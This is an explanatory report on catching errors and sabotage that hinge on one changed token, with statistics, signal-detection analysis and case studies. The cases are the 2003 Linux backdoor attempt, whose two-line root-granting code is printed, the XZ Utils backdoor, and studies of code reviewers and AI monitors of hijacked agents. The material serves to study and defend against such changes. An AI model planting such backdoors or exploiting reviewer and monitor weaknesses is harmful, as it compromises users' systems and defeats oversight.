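# Overseeing Outputs Where One Changed Token Decides Correctness

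## Outputs in which one token decides correctness

Editors, accountants, lawyers and programmers have long checked written work before anyone relies on it, and AI systems now do some of the writing and some of the checking. A small slip does little damage in most writing, but sometimes a single symbol determines whether the whole thing is right, and the checker has to notice that tiny difference. Here are three such differences, with the correct version first in each pair.

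- A program keeps a list with 100 places, numbered 0 to 99. The test `if (i < 100)` admits only places that exist. The test `if (i <= 100)` also admits place 100, which does not.
- "The supplier shall not be liable for late delivery." "The supplier shall be liable for late delivery."
- A loan of 200,000 at 4.5% a year costs 9,000 in interest in the first year. At 45% it costs 90,000.

None of the second versions looks broken. The program still runs, the clause is still good English, and some lenders do charge 45%.

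In this report, a *token* is a single word, symbol, number or operator. This is looser than the engineering sense, in which tokens are the pieces a language model splits text into, many of them fragments of words. A *decisive change* is a change to one or a few tokens, accidental or deliberate, that makes a correct output incorrect. A *high-sensitivity output* is one in which such a change is possible. A contract is high-sensitivity because a slight change to a few of its words would leave someone worse off, even though many of its other words could change slightly without harming anyone.

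Programmers often make errors this small. Karampatsis and Sutton (2019), in *How Often Do Single-Statement Bugs Occur?*, searched the histories of popular open-source Java projects for single-statement fixes that matched any of 16 templates, such as a wrong number, a swapped operator or a missing `!` (the symbol for "not"). They found about one such bug for every 1,600 to 2,500 lines of code. Richter and Wehrheim (2022), in *TSSB-3M*, collected more than 3 million Python fixes that each change only one statement. About 97,000 replace a number and 29,000 replace an operator that joins or compares two values. Another 740,000 change one token in a way that fits none of the dataset's named patterns. Both teams identified fixes by words like "fix" or "bug" in the programmer's note on the change, so the counts are rough, and they cover only errors that somebody noticed.

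A one-word change introduced a flaw in pyjwt, a Python library that checks the signed digital passes websites use to recognise their users. Version 2.10.0 replaced `list` with `Sequence` in the line that decides how to compare a pass's issuer with the expected issuer. In Python, text counts as a sequence but not as a list. An entry in GCVE's *CWE-697*, a public listing of comparison flaws, explains that the library therefore began to check whether the issuer's name appeared inside the expected name, instead of whether the two were equal, so a fragment of the expected name would be accepted.

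### Accident and intent

The entry treats the pyjwt change as an ordinary bug, and there is no reason to think otherwise. But the code would be the same if someone had made the change deliberately. In general, finding a decisive change rarely reveals why it is there.

In February 2026, developers repaired a flaw in the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, that let an ordinary user take full control of a machine. According to Paganini (2026), in *CVE-2026-23111*, they fixed it by deleting one `!`. Paganini describes the flaw as a logic error, whereas in 2003 somebody used a change about as small to try to plant a *backdoor*, a deliberate flaw that gives someone hidden access or control, in the same kernel.

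In 1631 the royal printers in London issued a Bible that omitted the word "not" from a commandment, making it read "Thou shalt commit adultery". Historians have since wondered whether a rival sabotaged the printing so that the printers would lose their licence. The printers never raised that possibility in their defence, and nobody can tell from the page whether the compositor left the word out by mistake or was bribed to do it.

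This simplifies the job of a *reviewer*, a person or AI model that examines an output and says whether something is wrong. (An AI reviewer is also called a monitor.) The reviewer first has to establish that the text is wrong. Motive is a later question and needs other evidence. Intent does matter for the statistics, because someone who makes a change on purpose chooses where to make it. The Java and Python collections therefore don't show how often deliberate changes occur or where.

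### Why averages and spot checks say little

If one line of a 2,000-line program is wrong, 99.95% of its lines are correct. That figure fairly describes the programmer's care, but it is almost useless for deciding whether the program works, because everything else may depend on the wrong line.

Because spreadsheet cells feed one another, a final figure can be unreliable even when each cell is probably right. Panko (2016), in *What We Don't Know About Spreadsheet Errors Today*, puts the average error rate in 14 laboratory studies at 3.9% of cells. Suppose a final figure depends on 100 cells, each with an independent 1% chance of being wrong. The chance that all 100 are right is 0.99^100, or 37%, so the final figure is probably wrong. At an error rate of 3.9%, the chance that it is wrong rises to 98%. Real spreadsheets are somewhat less fragile, because errors are not independent and some don't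 affect the final figure. Still, Panko reports that auditors and other inspectors found errors in 94% of the 85 working spreadsheets they examined intensively.

Spot checks have a related weakness. Suppose a reviewer reads 200 randomly chosen lines of the 2,000-line program and recognises any error in them. If the program has one wrong line, the reviewer has a 10% chance of finding it. If it has 20 wrong lines, each has a 90% chance of being outside the sample, and the chance that all of them are is roughly 0.9 to the 20th power, or 12%. The reviewer therefore has about an 88% chance of finding at least one.

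The spot check is therefore a decent way to detect sloppy work, but a very poor test of correctness. A reviewer who initially saw a 50% chance that the program contained one wrong line should still put the chance at about 47% after reading 200 of its 2,000 lines and finding no error. To have a 90% chance of encountering a lone error, the reviewer would have to read 1,800 lines. Starting with the lines that most affect the result works better than choosing lines at random, provided the reviewer knows which lines those are.

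### Counting hits and false alarms

If sampling is not enough, a reviewer has to look at everything. Judging how good the reviewer is then requires four numbers.

The *detection rate* is the share of errors that the reviewer flags. Computer scientists call it recall and doctors call it sensitivity, but this meaning of "sensitivity" is unrelated to the one in "high-sensitivity outputs". The *false-alarm rate* is the share of correct items that the reviewer flags. *Prevalence* is the share of reviewed items that contain an error. *Precision* is the share of flagged items that contain an error.

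Suppose a company makes 10,000 changes to its software and 10 of them (0.1%) are faulty. The reviewer catches 80% of the faulty changes and wrongly flags 5% of the correct ones.

| | Faulty changes | Sound changes | All changes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 8 | about 500 | about 508 |
| Passed | 2 | about 9,490 | about 9,492 |
| Total | 10 | 9,990 | 10,000 |

Eight of about 508 flags are correct, a precision of 1.6%. Accuracy is the wrong measure here because the reviewer correctly judges about 95% of the 10,000 changes, while one who flagged nothing would correctly judge about 99.9%. *Reasoning-Enhanced Rare-Event Prediction with Balanced Outcome Correction* (2026) makes the same point about prediction models, which can reach 99% accuracy on rare events without catching any.

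With p for prevalence, D for the detection rate and F for the false-alarm rate, the general formula is

$$\text{precision} = \frac{pD}{pD + (1-p)F}$$

When errors are rare and false alarms are not, precision is roughly p × D/F. In the example, a perfect detection rate would raise precision only from 1.6% to 2.0%, while halving the false-alarm rate would nearly double it. For half of the flags to mark real errors, the reviewer could raise only about 8 false alarms in 9,990 sound changes, a rate of 0.08%.

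Although only about 1.6% of the flagged changes are faulty, a careful second look at them may be well worth the effort, because the reviewer has reduced 10,000 changes to about 508 and kept 8 of the 10 faulty ones. A low rate becomes a problem when there are too many flags for anyone to take seriously. Karampatsis and Sutton ran SpotBugs, a program that scans Java code for likely errors, over their collection with every warning switched on, and it flagged about 12% of the template bugs among more than 200 million warnings.

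Precision depends on both the reviewer and the pile being reviewed. *Who Wrote This?* (2026) gives the example of a detector of AI-written essays with a false-alarm rate of 5%. If 100 essays in 10,000 come from an AI, the detector correctly flags 95 of them and wrongly flags about 495 human essays, so its precision is about 16%. If half the essays come from an AI, the same detector's precision is 95%. People are bad at allowing for this, a failing psychologists call base-rate neglect. *Biased Minds Meet Biased AI* (2025) explains it with the standard example of breast-cancer screening. A mammogram with a detection rate of 80% and a false-alarm rate of 10% sounds trustworthy, but if 1% of the women screened have cancer, only about 7% of those who test positive have it.

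Tests of working detectors show the same drop in precision when attacks are rare. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (2026) examines programs that monitor AI agents, which are language models that carry out tasks step by step, for signs that an outsider has taken them over. One detector would score a random attacked run as more suspicious than a random harmless run 88% of the time. With attacks in 2% of runs and a threshold meant to catch 80% of them, it raised 12.2 false alerts for every true one. If attacks occurred in 0.1% of runs, only 0.4% of its alerts would be true.

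Precision also depended on the choice of harmless runs. At 2% prevalence, it was 11.7% when the harmless runs were all ordinary and 3.9% when they were all hard cases. The lower figure is probably more worrying for decisive changes, because every faulty version has a correct counterpart that looks almost identical.

### Discriminability and criterion

Detection rates and false-alarm rates tend to move together. A reviewer who is quicker to flag outputs flags more correct ones as well as more incorrect ones, and so catches more errors without being any better at recognising them. Signal detection theory, which psychologists have used since the 1960s, separates the ability to recognise errors from the readiness to flag outputs.

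The theory treats the reviewer as forming an impression of how suspicious each item is and flagging the item when that impression passes a threshold. Faulty items give stronger impressions on average, but the two groups overlap. *Discriminability*, written d', is how far apart the groups lie, measured in units of their spread. The *criterion*, written c, is where the reviewer puts the threshold, measured from the midpoint between them. In plainer words, d' is how well the reviewer separates faulty from sound items, and c is how much evidence the reviewer demands before flagging. *Sensitivity or Criterion?* (2026) gives the usual formulas, in which H is the detection rate and FA the false-alarm rate:

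$$d' = z(H) - z(FA), \qquad c = -\tfrac{1}{2}\,\bigl(z(H) + z(FA)\bigr)$$

The function z converts a rate into a distance on the standard bell curve. It gives 0 for 50%, 0.84 for 80% and −1.64 for 5%. The reviewer of the 10,000 changes therefore has a d' of 0.84 + 1.64, or about 2.49, and a c of 0.40. A positive c means the reviewer flags cautiously. The same reviewer could move the threshold without changing d'.

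| Criterion c | Detection rate | False-alarm rate | Flags in 10,000 changes | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 89% | 10.7% | about 1,077 | 0.8% |
| 0.40 | 80% | 5% | about 508 | 1.6% |
| 1.00 | 60% | 1.2% | about 130 | 4.6% |

The reviewers in all three rows are equally skilled, but the first has the highest detection rate and the last has the highest precision, so either measure alone would make one reviewer look better than the others.

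*Beyond Accuracy* (Chen, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) reports an experiment in which accuracy alone was misleading. Five AI reviewers judged restaurant recommendations against a customer's stated requirements. Half of the recommendations contained a *planted error*, a known error inserted to test detection. The researchers varied how elaborately the recommending assistant described its own checking, and whether each customer review carried the name of its restaurant. Without those names, accuracy fell from 80% to 70% as the descriptions grew more elaborate, because the reviewers became more inclined to report errors, three of the five much more so than the others. False alarms rose from 39% to 60%, and c, which measures bias toward or against reporting an error, went from −0.94 to −1.58. The detection rate stayed at 99% to 100%, and d', which measures the ability to tell flawed recommendations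 from sound ones, rose from 2.42 to 2.68.

A reviewer with a low d' needs replacing or better information, while one with a badly placed criterion may only need to adjust it. Caruso, Fox and colleagues (2026) note in *The role of feedback in the low-prevalence effect* that people's criteria shift towards passing everything when targets become rare, and miss rates can climb from 10% to 30% or 40%.

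### Redundancy

Discriminability depends on both the reviewer's ability and the text. An output is easier to oversee when the same fact appears elsewhere, or when a reader can compute it from other information, because a change in one place then creates a contradiction. A cheque, for example, gives its amount in both words and figures. A loan agreement that sets the interest at 45% but lists a first-year charge of 9,000 on 200,000 contradicts itself, since 9,000 is 4.5% of 200,000.

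The Linux flaw of 2026 contained a contradiction of this kind. The faulty function restores certain entries in the kernel's packet filter after an operation fails. It should have skipped active entries and processed inactive ones, but it did the opposite. The official description, in Debian's *CVE-2026-23111*, compares it with a function that does the same job for other entries and performs the check correctly. The rest of that description, in OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-23111* (2026), explains that removing the negation from the faulty check made the two functions agree.

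A contradiction does not by itself show which side is wrong. The sibling function might have been the faulty one, and the official description also cites what the function logically has to do. Someone has to compare the two statements. Both functions were in public source code, and Paganini dates the discovery to early 2025, about a year before the repair. The second statement must also be independent of the first. If a clerk calculates the interest charge from the mistaken rate, the agreement will list 90,000 and contain no contradiction.

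The restaurant experiment gives some idea of how much redundancy can help. Chen and colleagues always displayed a customer review that contradicted the planted error, and 98% of the catches named the requirement that the recommendation actually violated. When the display didn't name the restaurant each review was about, reviewers complained in about 60% of the false alarms that they could not match the evidence to a restaurant. Adding the name eliminated that complaint, and in the most suspicious of the five models it cut false alarms from 96% to 65% under the most elaborate description. The test was small, with 19 tasks of one type. Because the evidence was always in view, it does not show how the same reviewers would do if they had to find the contradiction themselves.

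When a fact such as an interest rate appears only once in a document and nothing else there depends on it, a reviewer can tell from the document only whether it is plausible. To check that it is correct, the reviewer needs a record that the change did not affect, such as the signed offer or the bank's file.

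## Comparing a change with a trusted record

A bank clerk who has the signed offer can check the rate in a loan agreement without knowing what rates are normal. The clerk only has to find what differs from the offer, which people already trust, and who approved the difference, rather than decide whether the agreement is correct.

A *diff* is a display of exactly what differs between two versions of a text. The program that makes it lines up the parts the versions share and prints the rest, usually with a minus sign before each old line and a plus sign before each new one. For the list with 100 places, it would print this:

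```
- if (i < 100)
+ if (i <= 100)
```

A reviewer who trusts the old version of a 2,000-line program can compare it with the new version and think about only the one line that changed. Lawyers compare drafts of a contract in the same way.

A computer can compare two copies that should be identical before anyone reads them. It calculates a *checksum*, a short number derived from the whole file, for each copy and checks whether the numbers match. With a well-designed checksum, changing a single character practically always changes the number, even if the character does not show on screen. Some characters are invisible or rearrange the text around them, so editors such as Visual Studio Code now highlight them. GCC and the Rust compiler, which translate source code into programs that a computer can run, also now warn about characters that reverse the direction of text.

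A diff that corrects `<=` to `<` is as short as one that introduces the error, so someone still has to judge which version is right, unless the two copies were supposed to match. In 2003, the Linux developers had two copies of their code that were supposed to match.

### The Linux attempt of 2003

The developers kept the master copy of the kernel in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them could not or would not use it, so BitKeeper's maker, BitMover, published a second copy through another system, CVS. Changes flowed only from BitKeeper to CVS. Each entry in the CVS history ended with a pointer, such as "(Logical change 1.14141)", to the matching change in BitKeeper. According to the blog Freedom to Tinker, the pointer led to the record of the change's approval.

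BitMover's founder described the safeguard in a discussion on the kernel developers' mailing list (McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*). Every night a script compared checksums of the public CVS files with those of BitMover's internal copy, and sent an email if they differed. On 5 November it flagged a file called `exit.c`. The file's history contained three new entries from the day before, all under the name of David Miller, a trusted kernel developer, who denied making them. None of the three had a pointer. Their net effect was to add two lines:

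```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines belonged to `wait4`, a function that lets one program wait for another to finish. They look like a check that returns an error if a program requests an odd pair of options and its user is number 0. User 0 is root, the account that may do anything on the machine. In C, the kernel's language, `==` compares two values, while `=` sets the left one to the right one. The code used `=`, so it made the user root instead of checking whether the user was root. Any program that called `wait4` with those two options would have gained complete control. Corbet (2003), in *The upcoming security fight*, corrected reports that the flaw worked over the internet, explaining that an attacker first had to be able to run a program on the machine.

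McVoy did not see this at first. His first message asked whoever had edited the file to own up, and said it was "not a big deal". Another developer asked, out of curiosity, which lines had changed, and McVoy posted the diff. Ten minutes later someone replied that it looked odd. Fifteen minutes after that, Chad Kitching wrote that it looked like an attempt to backdoor the kernel. McVoy answered, "Good eyes, I missed that," and pointed out the single equals sign.

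The comparison revealed the change before anybody understood it. McVoy knew that somebody had edited the file improperly and had only two lines to read, but he still missed the error. Without the comparison, a reader would have had to find those two lines among millions. Linus Torvalds, the creator of Linux, put the number at five million in an email that appears in Miller and Barr's *Linux kernel development process thwarts subversion attempt*.

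Kitching noticed another clue in the text, which was that the next line of the function overwrote the error code, so the supposed check would have achieved nothing even with `==`. But a reader who spotted all this might still have taken it for a mistake. Ryan Russell, a security consultant quoted in *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* (Poulsen, 2003), called the change "indistinguishable from an accidental bug" for anyone without a reason to check whether it had arrived legitimately.

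BitMover had also been worried about accidents. In August 2003, after users found out-of-date files in the CVS copy, McVoy announced in *BK2CVS problem (fixed)* a validation script that exported both copies and ran a diff on them. He did not say whether this script became the November check.

McVoy and Torvalds disagreed about how close the backdoor came to a real release. McVoy thought that a developer working from the CVS copy could have unknowingly submitted the two lines with other work. Torvalds replied that the lines had no route into a release, because he or his colleagues would read patches sent by email, and the people who merged changes through BitKeeper did not use the CVS copy. Torvalds is probably right. A developer who started from the tampered file and made a diff against it would have sent a patch without the two lines, because both sides of the diff would have contained them.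 The patch would have included them only if the developer had compared the work with a clean version.

The public BitKeeper copy had its own protection. Torvalds worked on a private copy and sent his changes to the public one. BitKeeper would refuse the transfer if the public copy contained a change that his lacked, so he would have discovered an intruder's change the next time he tried to publish.

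### Names, signatures and second approvals

The three false entries carried Miller's name, but that didn't prove Miller wrote them. A *digital signature* is harder to fake than a name. The author of a change uses a secret key to compute the signature from the text, and anyone with the matching public key can check it. If somebody alters even one character of the text afterwards, the check fails.

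Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, had been asking McVoy for years to add signatures to BitKeeper. In the 2003 discussion he described a danger that the nightly comparison could not address. Someone might forge an email from a trusted developer, offering a small bug fix that opened a security hole, and Torvalds might accept it into the master copy. If every change carried a signature, anyone could verify it at any time, not only the person who received it. McVoy agreed, and wrote that he already had a design and had been waiting for some event to justify it.

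A signature does not show that anybody other than the author has looked at the change, so many projects require a second person to approve each change before it enters the master copy. An error in XZ Utils, a set of file-compression programs found on most Linux systems, shows why approval should come first. In May 2023 a change replaced `==` with `>=` in two places. Lasse Collin, the project's original maintainer, objected in a chat, but slightly too late to keep the error out of the master copy. A second change then reversed it. Collin describes the error in his review notes on the website of Tukaani, the project behind XZ. He wrote those notes because of a much larger failure of approval.

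### XZ Utils: release files that differed from the public source

On 29 March 2024 the software developer Andres Freund disclosed, in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), that XZ Utils contained a backdoor. He found it by investigating odd symptoms rather than by comparing files. Over several weeks, he had noticed problems on machines running a development version of Debian, a widely used Linux system. Logins through SSH, the standard tool for remote access, were using a lot of processor time, and Valgrind, a program that checks for memory errors, was reporting some. A login attempt that should have failed in 0.299 seconds took 0.807. Freund traced the extra half second to XZ's compression library. He first suspected that someone had tampered with Debian's package, then found that the fault came from the XZ project itself.

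Like many projects, XZ published its source in two forms. The public repository held the code with its full history, and release files packaged each version for the people who build Linux systems. Most of the backdoor was in the repository, in files that were supposedly test data, but the part that activated it was only in the release files. A build script there contained a line that Freund could not find in the repository or in the script's original source. A diff between the release and the repository would have shown that line.

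Comparing the XZ release files with the repository would also have shown many other differences. According to an entry in the vulnerability database of CIRCL, Luxembourg's computer-incident centre, release files commonly differ from the repository in projects written in C, because developers add generated build scripts to spare users a step. A reviewer who treated every difference as suspicious would have flagged many legitimate projects. The 2003 Linux comparison worked so well because the two copies had no legitimate reason to differ. For XZ, the same method would have had an equally high detection rate but very low precision.

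Reducing the number of legitimate differences can improve precision. Collin has since decided to leave generated documentation out of the release files, partly for this reason and partly to simplify licensing.

Checking signatures would not have exposed the bad release files. Collin (2024), in *xz backdoor*, reports that his co-maintainer, who used the name Jia Tan, had created and signed them, so a signature check would have correctly shown that they came from an authorised maintainer. Freund thought it less likely that an intruder had taken over the maintainer's system than that the maintainer was responsible, because the same person had been discussing supposed fixes for the resulting errors on several mailing lists. The signature would have been valid in either case. In a later mailing-list discussion, *New supply-chain security tool*, one participant concluded that developers' signatures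 were "overrated" and that people needed to know what was in the code more than who had supplied it.

### Rebuilding programs from source

Reviewers read source code, but users run the machine instructions a compiler makes from it, which hardly anyone reads. Someone could alter the finished program without changing the reviewed source.

Reproducible builds close this gap. *Debian 14* (heise) defines a package as reproducible if identical source code and the same build environment produce a bit-identical result. When Debian first builds a package, it records the build environment in a small file. A separate service, reproduce.debian.net, uses that file to recreate the environment, rebuilds the package and compares the two results bit by bit. The service went into operation during the year before February 2026, according to Reproducible Builds (2026), the project that develops its software.

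In May 2026 Debian made the comparison a rule. Gevers (2026), in *bits from the release team*, announced that Debian's software would now keep new packages out of "testing", the collection that becomes the next stable version, if nobody could reproduce them. It would also block updates that made packages already in testing no longer reproducible. In a follow-up, Gevers said there would be exceptions and that he hoped their number would shrink.

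The second part of the rule is probably more useful for finding tampering. Linuxiac's *Debian Now Blocks Non-Reproducible Packages from Testing* reports that over 98% of builds were reproduced, or 23,728 packages, which leaves up to about 480 that were not. Most of these will have failed for ordinary reasons, such as a build that writes the current time into its output. If one of the 480 had been tampered with, each package a reviewer checked would have about a 0.2% chance of being that one. The list of packages that matched last month but do not match today is much shorter.

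Catching the XZ backdoor by comparison required checking the developers' release files against the project's repository. Debian built XZ from the release files, so a second build from the same files should have produced the same backdoored program. Checking Debian's copy against the developers' release file would also have missed the backdoor. Debaudit, a service for checking Debian source packages that Lucas Nussbaum announced in March 2026, includes this check (Giraud, 2026). XZ would have passed it because the developers' own file contained the backdoor.

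Rebuilding also depends on a sound compiler. Ken Thompson, a creator of the Unix operating system, showed in 1984 that a compiler could insert a backdoor into the programs it translated. Two builds made with the same bad compiler would match, so comparing them would not reveal the backdoor.

### When the trusted copy is wrong

The day after Freund's disclosure, people searching through XZ's history found a stray full stop in the repository itself, which even a comparison with the repository would not have revealed. sjw (2024) pointed it out in a reply to Freund's message, crediting commenters on the code-hosting site GitHub.

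XZ can use Landlock, a Linux feature that limits what a program may do if an attacker takes it over. A file of XZ's build instructions contains a very short program that tests whether the system supports Landlock. If the program compiles, the build process switches the protection on. A full stop alone on one line made the test program invalid C, so the test always failed and XZ was built without the protection. The person building it would get no warning unless they had explicitly demanded Landlock.

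Jia Tan had made the change in February 2024 and described it as a fix for the Landlock test. Collin removed the full stop on 30 March with a one-line patch (*CMake: Fix sabotaged Landlock sandbox check*, 2024). In his review notes, he wrote that the change has a "." at the beginning of a line that "sabotages the Landlock detection". The practical harm was probably small, because the full stop was only in version 5.6.1 and sjw knew of no Linux distribution that built XZ with those instructions.

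Comparing the records would not have flagged this change, because the release and the repository matched and the change came from someone with the authority to make it. Judging from the line alone, it could still be a typo. Collin's word "sabotaged" is based on everything else the same account had done.

He then had to recheck work that he had already accepted. His notes cover changes from December 2022 to March 2024, and he published a first complete version two months after the disclosure. Most of the verdicts are "OK". Removing the malicious files from the history would have required dropping only eight changes. He also listed ordinary mistakes, including a `<` from July 2023 that should have been `<=` in a check on memory use. It made no practical difference because the program was counting in single bytes. An approval record saves work by letting people skip what a trusted colleague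 has already passed, but Collin could no longer skip any change his co-maintainer had touched.

A stolen account creates the same difficulty. The thief's changes arrive with the right name and, if the thief also has the key, a valid signature. Requiring a second person's approval makes this harder, since the thief must also deceive or impersonate someone else. But the second person still has to read the diff. The diff for the Landlock test added 22 lines to the build instructions, and one of them contained only the full stop. David Andersen, a reader commenting on Anderson's post about Collin's fix, wrote that he had looked at the diff and not seen the full stop, "despite having been primed to look for something evil".

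## How well people find a rare error by reading

Andersen missed the full stop even though the diff was short and he had good reason to expect sabotage. Reviewers usually have less to go on, because nobody has told them that anything is wrong and most of what they read is fine. Researchers measure how many errors such readers catch by planting errors in code and asking programmers to review it. Most of these errors are small security flaws, often about a line long, and some are omitted checks. The results are therefore only a rough guide to how often reviewers catch a single changed token.

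In the closest experiment, reported in *First Come First Served* (2022), 106 participants reviewed code with two planted errors, and about half missed each one. Fifty noticed a missing `break`, a one-word command that ends a loop or a branch of a program. Fifty-two noticed a corner case, an unusual situation that the code handled wrongly.

### What a warning changes

In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues studied why reviewers miss flaws that are easy to understand and fix. Their 146 participants, 105 of whom had at least three years of professional experience, reviewed a change of about 140 lines to a Java program that manages employees' holidays. The instructions did not mention security. Each participant received one of two versions at random.

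In one version, the program pasted whatever a user typed as an employee number straight into a database query, so a user who typed a fragment of a query could change what the database did. This is called SQL injection and is a textbook example of a security flaw. In the other version, the program let employees buy extra days of holiday without checking that the number of days was positive, so an employee who bought minus five days would receive money instead of paying it.

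Of the 80 participants whose code had the SQL flaw, 52 (65%) found it. Of the 66 whose code had the holiday flaw, 14 (21%) found it. The paper describes the SQL flaw as seven times more likely to be found, but that figure is a ratio of odds (the number of people who found a flaw divided by the number who did not). The share of people who found the SQL flaw was about three times the share who found the holiday flaw.

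The holiday flaw is no harder to fix than the SQL flaw, since one short condition would do it. But people who spotted the SQL flaw often said they had seen the pattern before. The holiday flaw follows no well-known pattern, so to find it, a reviewer has to consider what would happen if somebody entered a negative number.

Braz and colleagues then told the participants that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind or where, and invited those who had missed it to look again. Another 13 people found the SQL flaw and 7 found the holiday flaw. The other 60 participants, 41% of the total, missed the flaw again, and 45 of them had code with the holiday flaw.

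Most of those who succeeded at the second attempt said they had needed a reminder to think about security. Those who never found the holiday flaw most often said they had not paid enough attention or had focused on other aspects of the code. Eight said they had mistaken a different error for the vulnerability. The researchers had also planted an ordinary bug to check that participants were making an effort, and 76 people found it in the first review. Finding it did not measurably reduce the chance of finding the security flaw in that review. After the warning, though, a reviewer who believed there was only one flaw and already had a candidate had little reason to keep looking.

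This experiment cannot fully separate the effect of the warning from the effect of reading the code twice, because everyone who tried again had also received the warning. A second experiment avoided this problem by giving people the instructions first and having them review only once.

### Asking reviewers to look for security flaws

Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022), in *Less is More*, randomly divided 150 participants into four groups. All of them reviewed the same 160-line change, which registered new users of a website and contained two flaws. One was an error message that wrote users' personal details to a log file. The other was the word `"MD5"` in the line that chose how to scramble passwords before storing them. MD5 is an old method that attackers can now break quickly. This flaw is about as close to a decisive change as any in these experiments, because a single word determines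 the method.

The first group received no instructions about security. The second heard that the researchers were interested in security issues. The third and fourth heard the same and also received a checklist.

| Instructions | Participants | Found the log flaw | Found MD5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing about security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security issues | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
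| The same, with a checklist of 22 items | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with a checklist of 7 items | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

Asking reviewers to look for security issues therefore made a very large difference. Many who would otherwise have passed these flaws were able to find them when asked. Three reviewers in the group without instructions said that finding the MD5 flaw was not part of their job, and one of them assumed that someone else would do a separate security assessment.

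The researchers found no statistically significant benefit from either checklist. This is surprising because both lists included items that pointed to the two flaws, and the short one contained nothing irrelevant to the code. With about 40 people in each group, the experiment could have missed a modest benefit, but the participants' comments suggest why any benefit was not large. Some ignored the list or read it only after finishing the review. Others lacked the knowledge to answer its questions correctly, including one who had considered MD5 and judged it a good choice.

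Neither experiment can show how many false alarms a security instruction causes, because every participant reviewed faulty code and the researchers scored only whether people reported the planted flaws. The instruction may have raised discriminability by directing attention to the lines that mattered, lowered the criterion so that reviewers reported more suspicions of every kind, or both. A message can lower the criterion without raising discriminability. In *Intrinsic motivation and false feedback reduce the low prevalence effect* (Kunar, Moronfolu and Jagota, 2025), volunteers who were falsely told that they were missing more tumours in breast scans than most people missed fewer tumours and raised more false alarms, with no significant change in discriminability (d').

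### Reviews in a working project

The participants in these experiments were reviewing a stranger's code with nothing at stake. Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021), in *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, examined real reviews from Chromium OS, the open-source project behind Google's Chromebook operating system. They searched about 405,000 reviews for comments on security and confirmed 516 in which somebody had caught a security defect. They also traced known defects to 374 reviews in which they had been missed.

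The reviewers' detection rate cannot be calculated as 516 out of 890, or 58%, because the researchers collected the caught and missed defects by different methods and nobody knows how many defects remain undiscovered. Medical researchers use the same design to compare people with and without a disease. It can show how the groups differ but not how common the disease is.

The defects that reviewers caught were very different in kind from those they missed. Reviewers caught all 53 uses of functions known to be dangerous and 65 of the 82 incorrect calculations. But they caught only 9 of the 81 failures to check input properly, the family that includes the holiday flaw, and only 3 of the 65 cases in which a program kept using something, such as a piece of memory, after giving it up. Paul and colleagues conclude that reviewers tend to catch defects that are visible in a few lines and to miss those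 that require running the code or understanding a larger part of it.

That conclusion is plausible, but the search may have exaggerated the contrast. It looked for comments containing any of 105 keywords, including "overflow", "race" and `strcpy` (one of the dangerous functions), so it was more likely to miss a comment such as "what if this is negative?"

The researchers also built a statistical model of what distinguished successful reviews. The odds of success were 4.55 times as high when the change was meant to fix a bug, perhaps because reviewers pay more attention to code that has already gone wrong. The most informative feature was the number of directories a change touched, and the odds fell as that number rose. Reviewers did better with files they had often reviewed and with code authors with whom they had exchanged reviews. Reviews that stayed open longer also succeeded more often,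 but the researchers measured the time from submission to decision, so a long review may have involved little extra reading.

Reviewers who had done more reviews in total were slightly less likely to catch a defect. Paul and colleagues suggest that these reviewers may have been tired or in a hurry, or that ordinary reviewing does not teach people to recognise security defects. Busy reviewers may also get the harder changes. The model cannot distinguish between these explanations.

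The number of reviewers made no detectable difference. However, *A security perspective on code review* (di Biase, Bruntink and Bacchelli, 2016), an earlier study of the related Chromium web browser, found early signs that reviews with more than two reviewers did better. Neither study assigned reviewers at random, so neither can settle whether adding readers helps catch decisive changes.

Di Biase and colleagues also read 1,155 randomly chosen reviewer comments on changes to the browser and found that about 1% concerned security. This suggests that reviewers seldom find a security flaw to report. The share of changes with flaws may not be 1%, because reviewers may have missed some flaws and commented several times on others.

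### Why people miss rare targets

People can miss things because they are rare. Psychologists call this the *low-prevalence effect* and have studied it mostly in visual search, where people look for a target such as a weapon in an X-rayed bag. Jeremy Wolfe's team found that people missed 7% of targets when half of the images contained one, and 30% when only 1% did, as recounted by Kunar and colleagues.

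The usual explanation is that people who see image after image without a target learn that "nothing there" is nearly always the right answer, so they give up sooner on each image and miss targets in the parts they haven't examined. They also demand more evidence before calling anything a target, so they may look straight at one and dismiss it. In signal detection theory, this stricter standard is a higher criterion c.

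Demanding more evidence before reporting an error can be reasonable. Suppose that a reviewer with a d' of 2.49 examines 10,000 items, of which 100 are faulty. With a lenient criterion, the reviewer misses 7 errors and raises about 1,540 false alarms. With a stricter one, the reviewer misses 30 errors and raises about 250 false alarms. The stricter criterion adds 23 missed errors but avoids about 1,290 false alarms, so it is the better choice unless a missed error does at least 56 times as much harm as a false alarm. A typing error in a comment does not do that much harm, but a change that lets any user take control of a machine very likely does, and a reviewer who has slipped into the strict criterion out of habit is then using the wrong one.

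The July 2026 meta-analysis by Caruso and colleagues, which combined 62 comparisons from 29 publications, gives the best estimate of the size of this shift. Each comparison was between a condition in which 1% to 30% of displays contained a target and one in which 40% to 60% did. When targets were rare, the criterion moved towards "nothing there" by 1.8 standard deviations, a very large effect in psychology. Discriminability did not reliably change.

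The shift was larger when the gap in prevalence was larger. It was also about one standard deviation larger when participants learned after every display whether they had been right. Feedback usually helps people improve, but when targets are rare, almost all of it confirms that "nothing there" was correct, so people learn to say it more readily.

Professional experience gave no clear protection. Caruso and colleagues found no significant difference between novices and professionals, who were radiologists and airport security officers.

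The true average shift is probably somewhat smaller than 1.8. Smaller studies tended to report larger shifts, which can happen when striking results are more likely to be published, and more than half of the eligible comparisons lacked the data needed to include them. The direction is much less doubtful. Allowing for differences between studies, the researchers expect 95% of future results to show a shift of between 0.1 and 3.5 towards "nothing there".

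### Boredom and wandering minds

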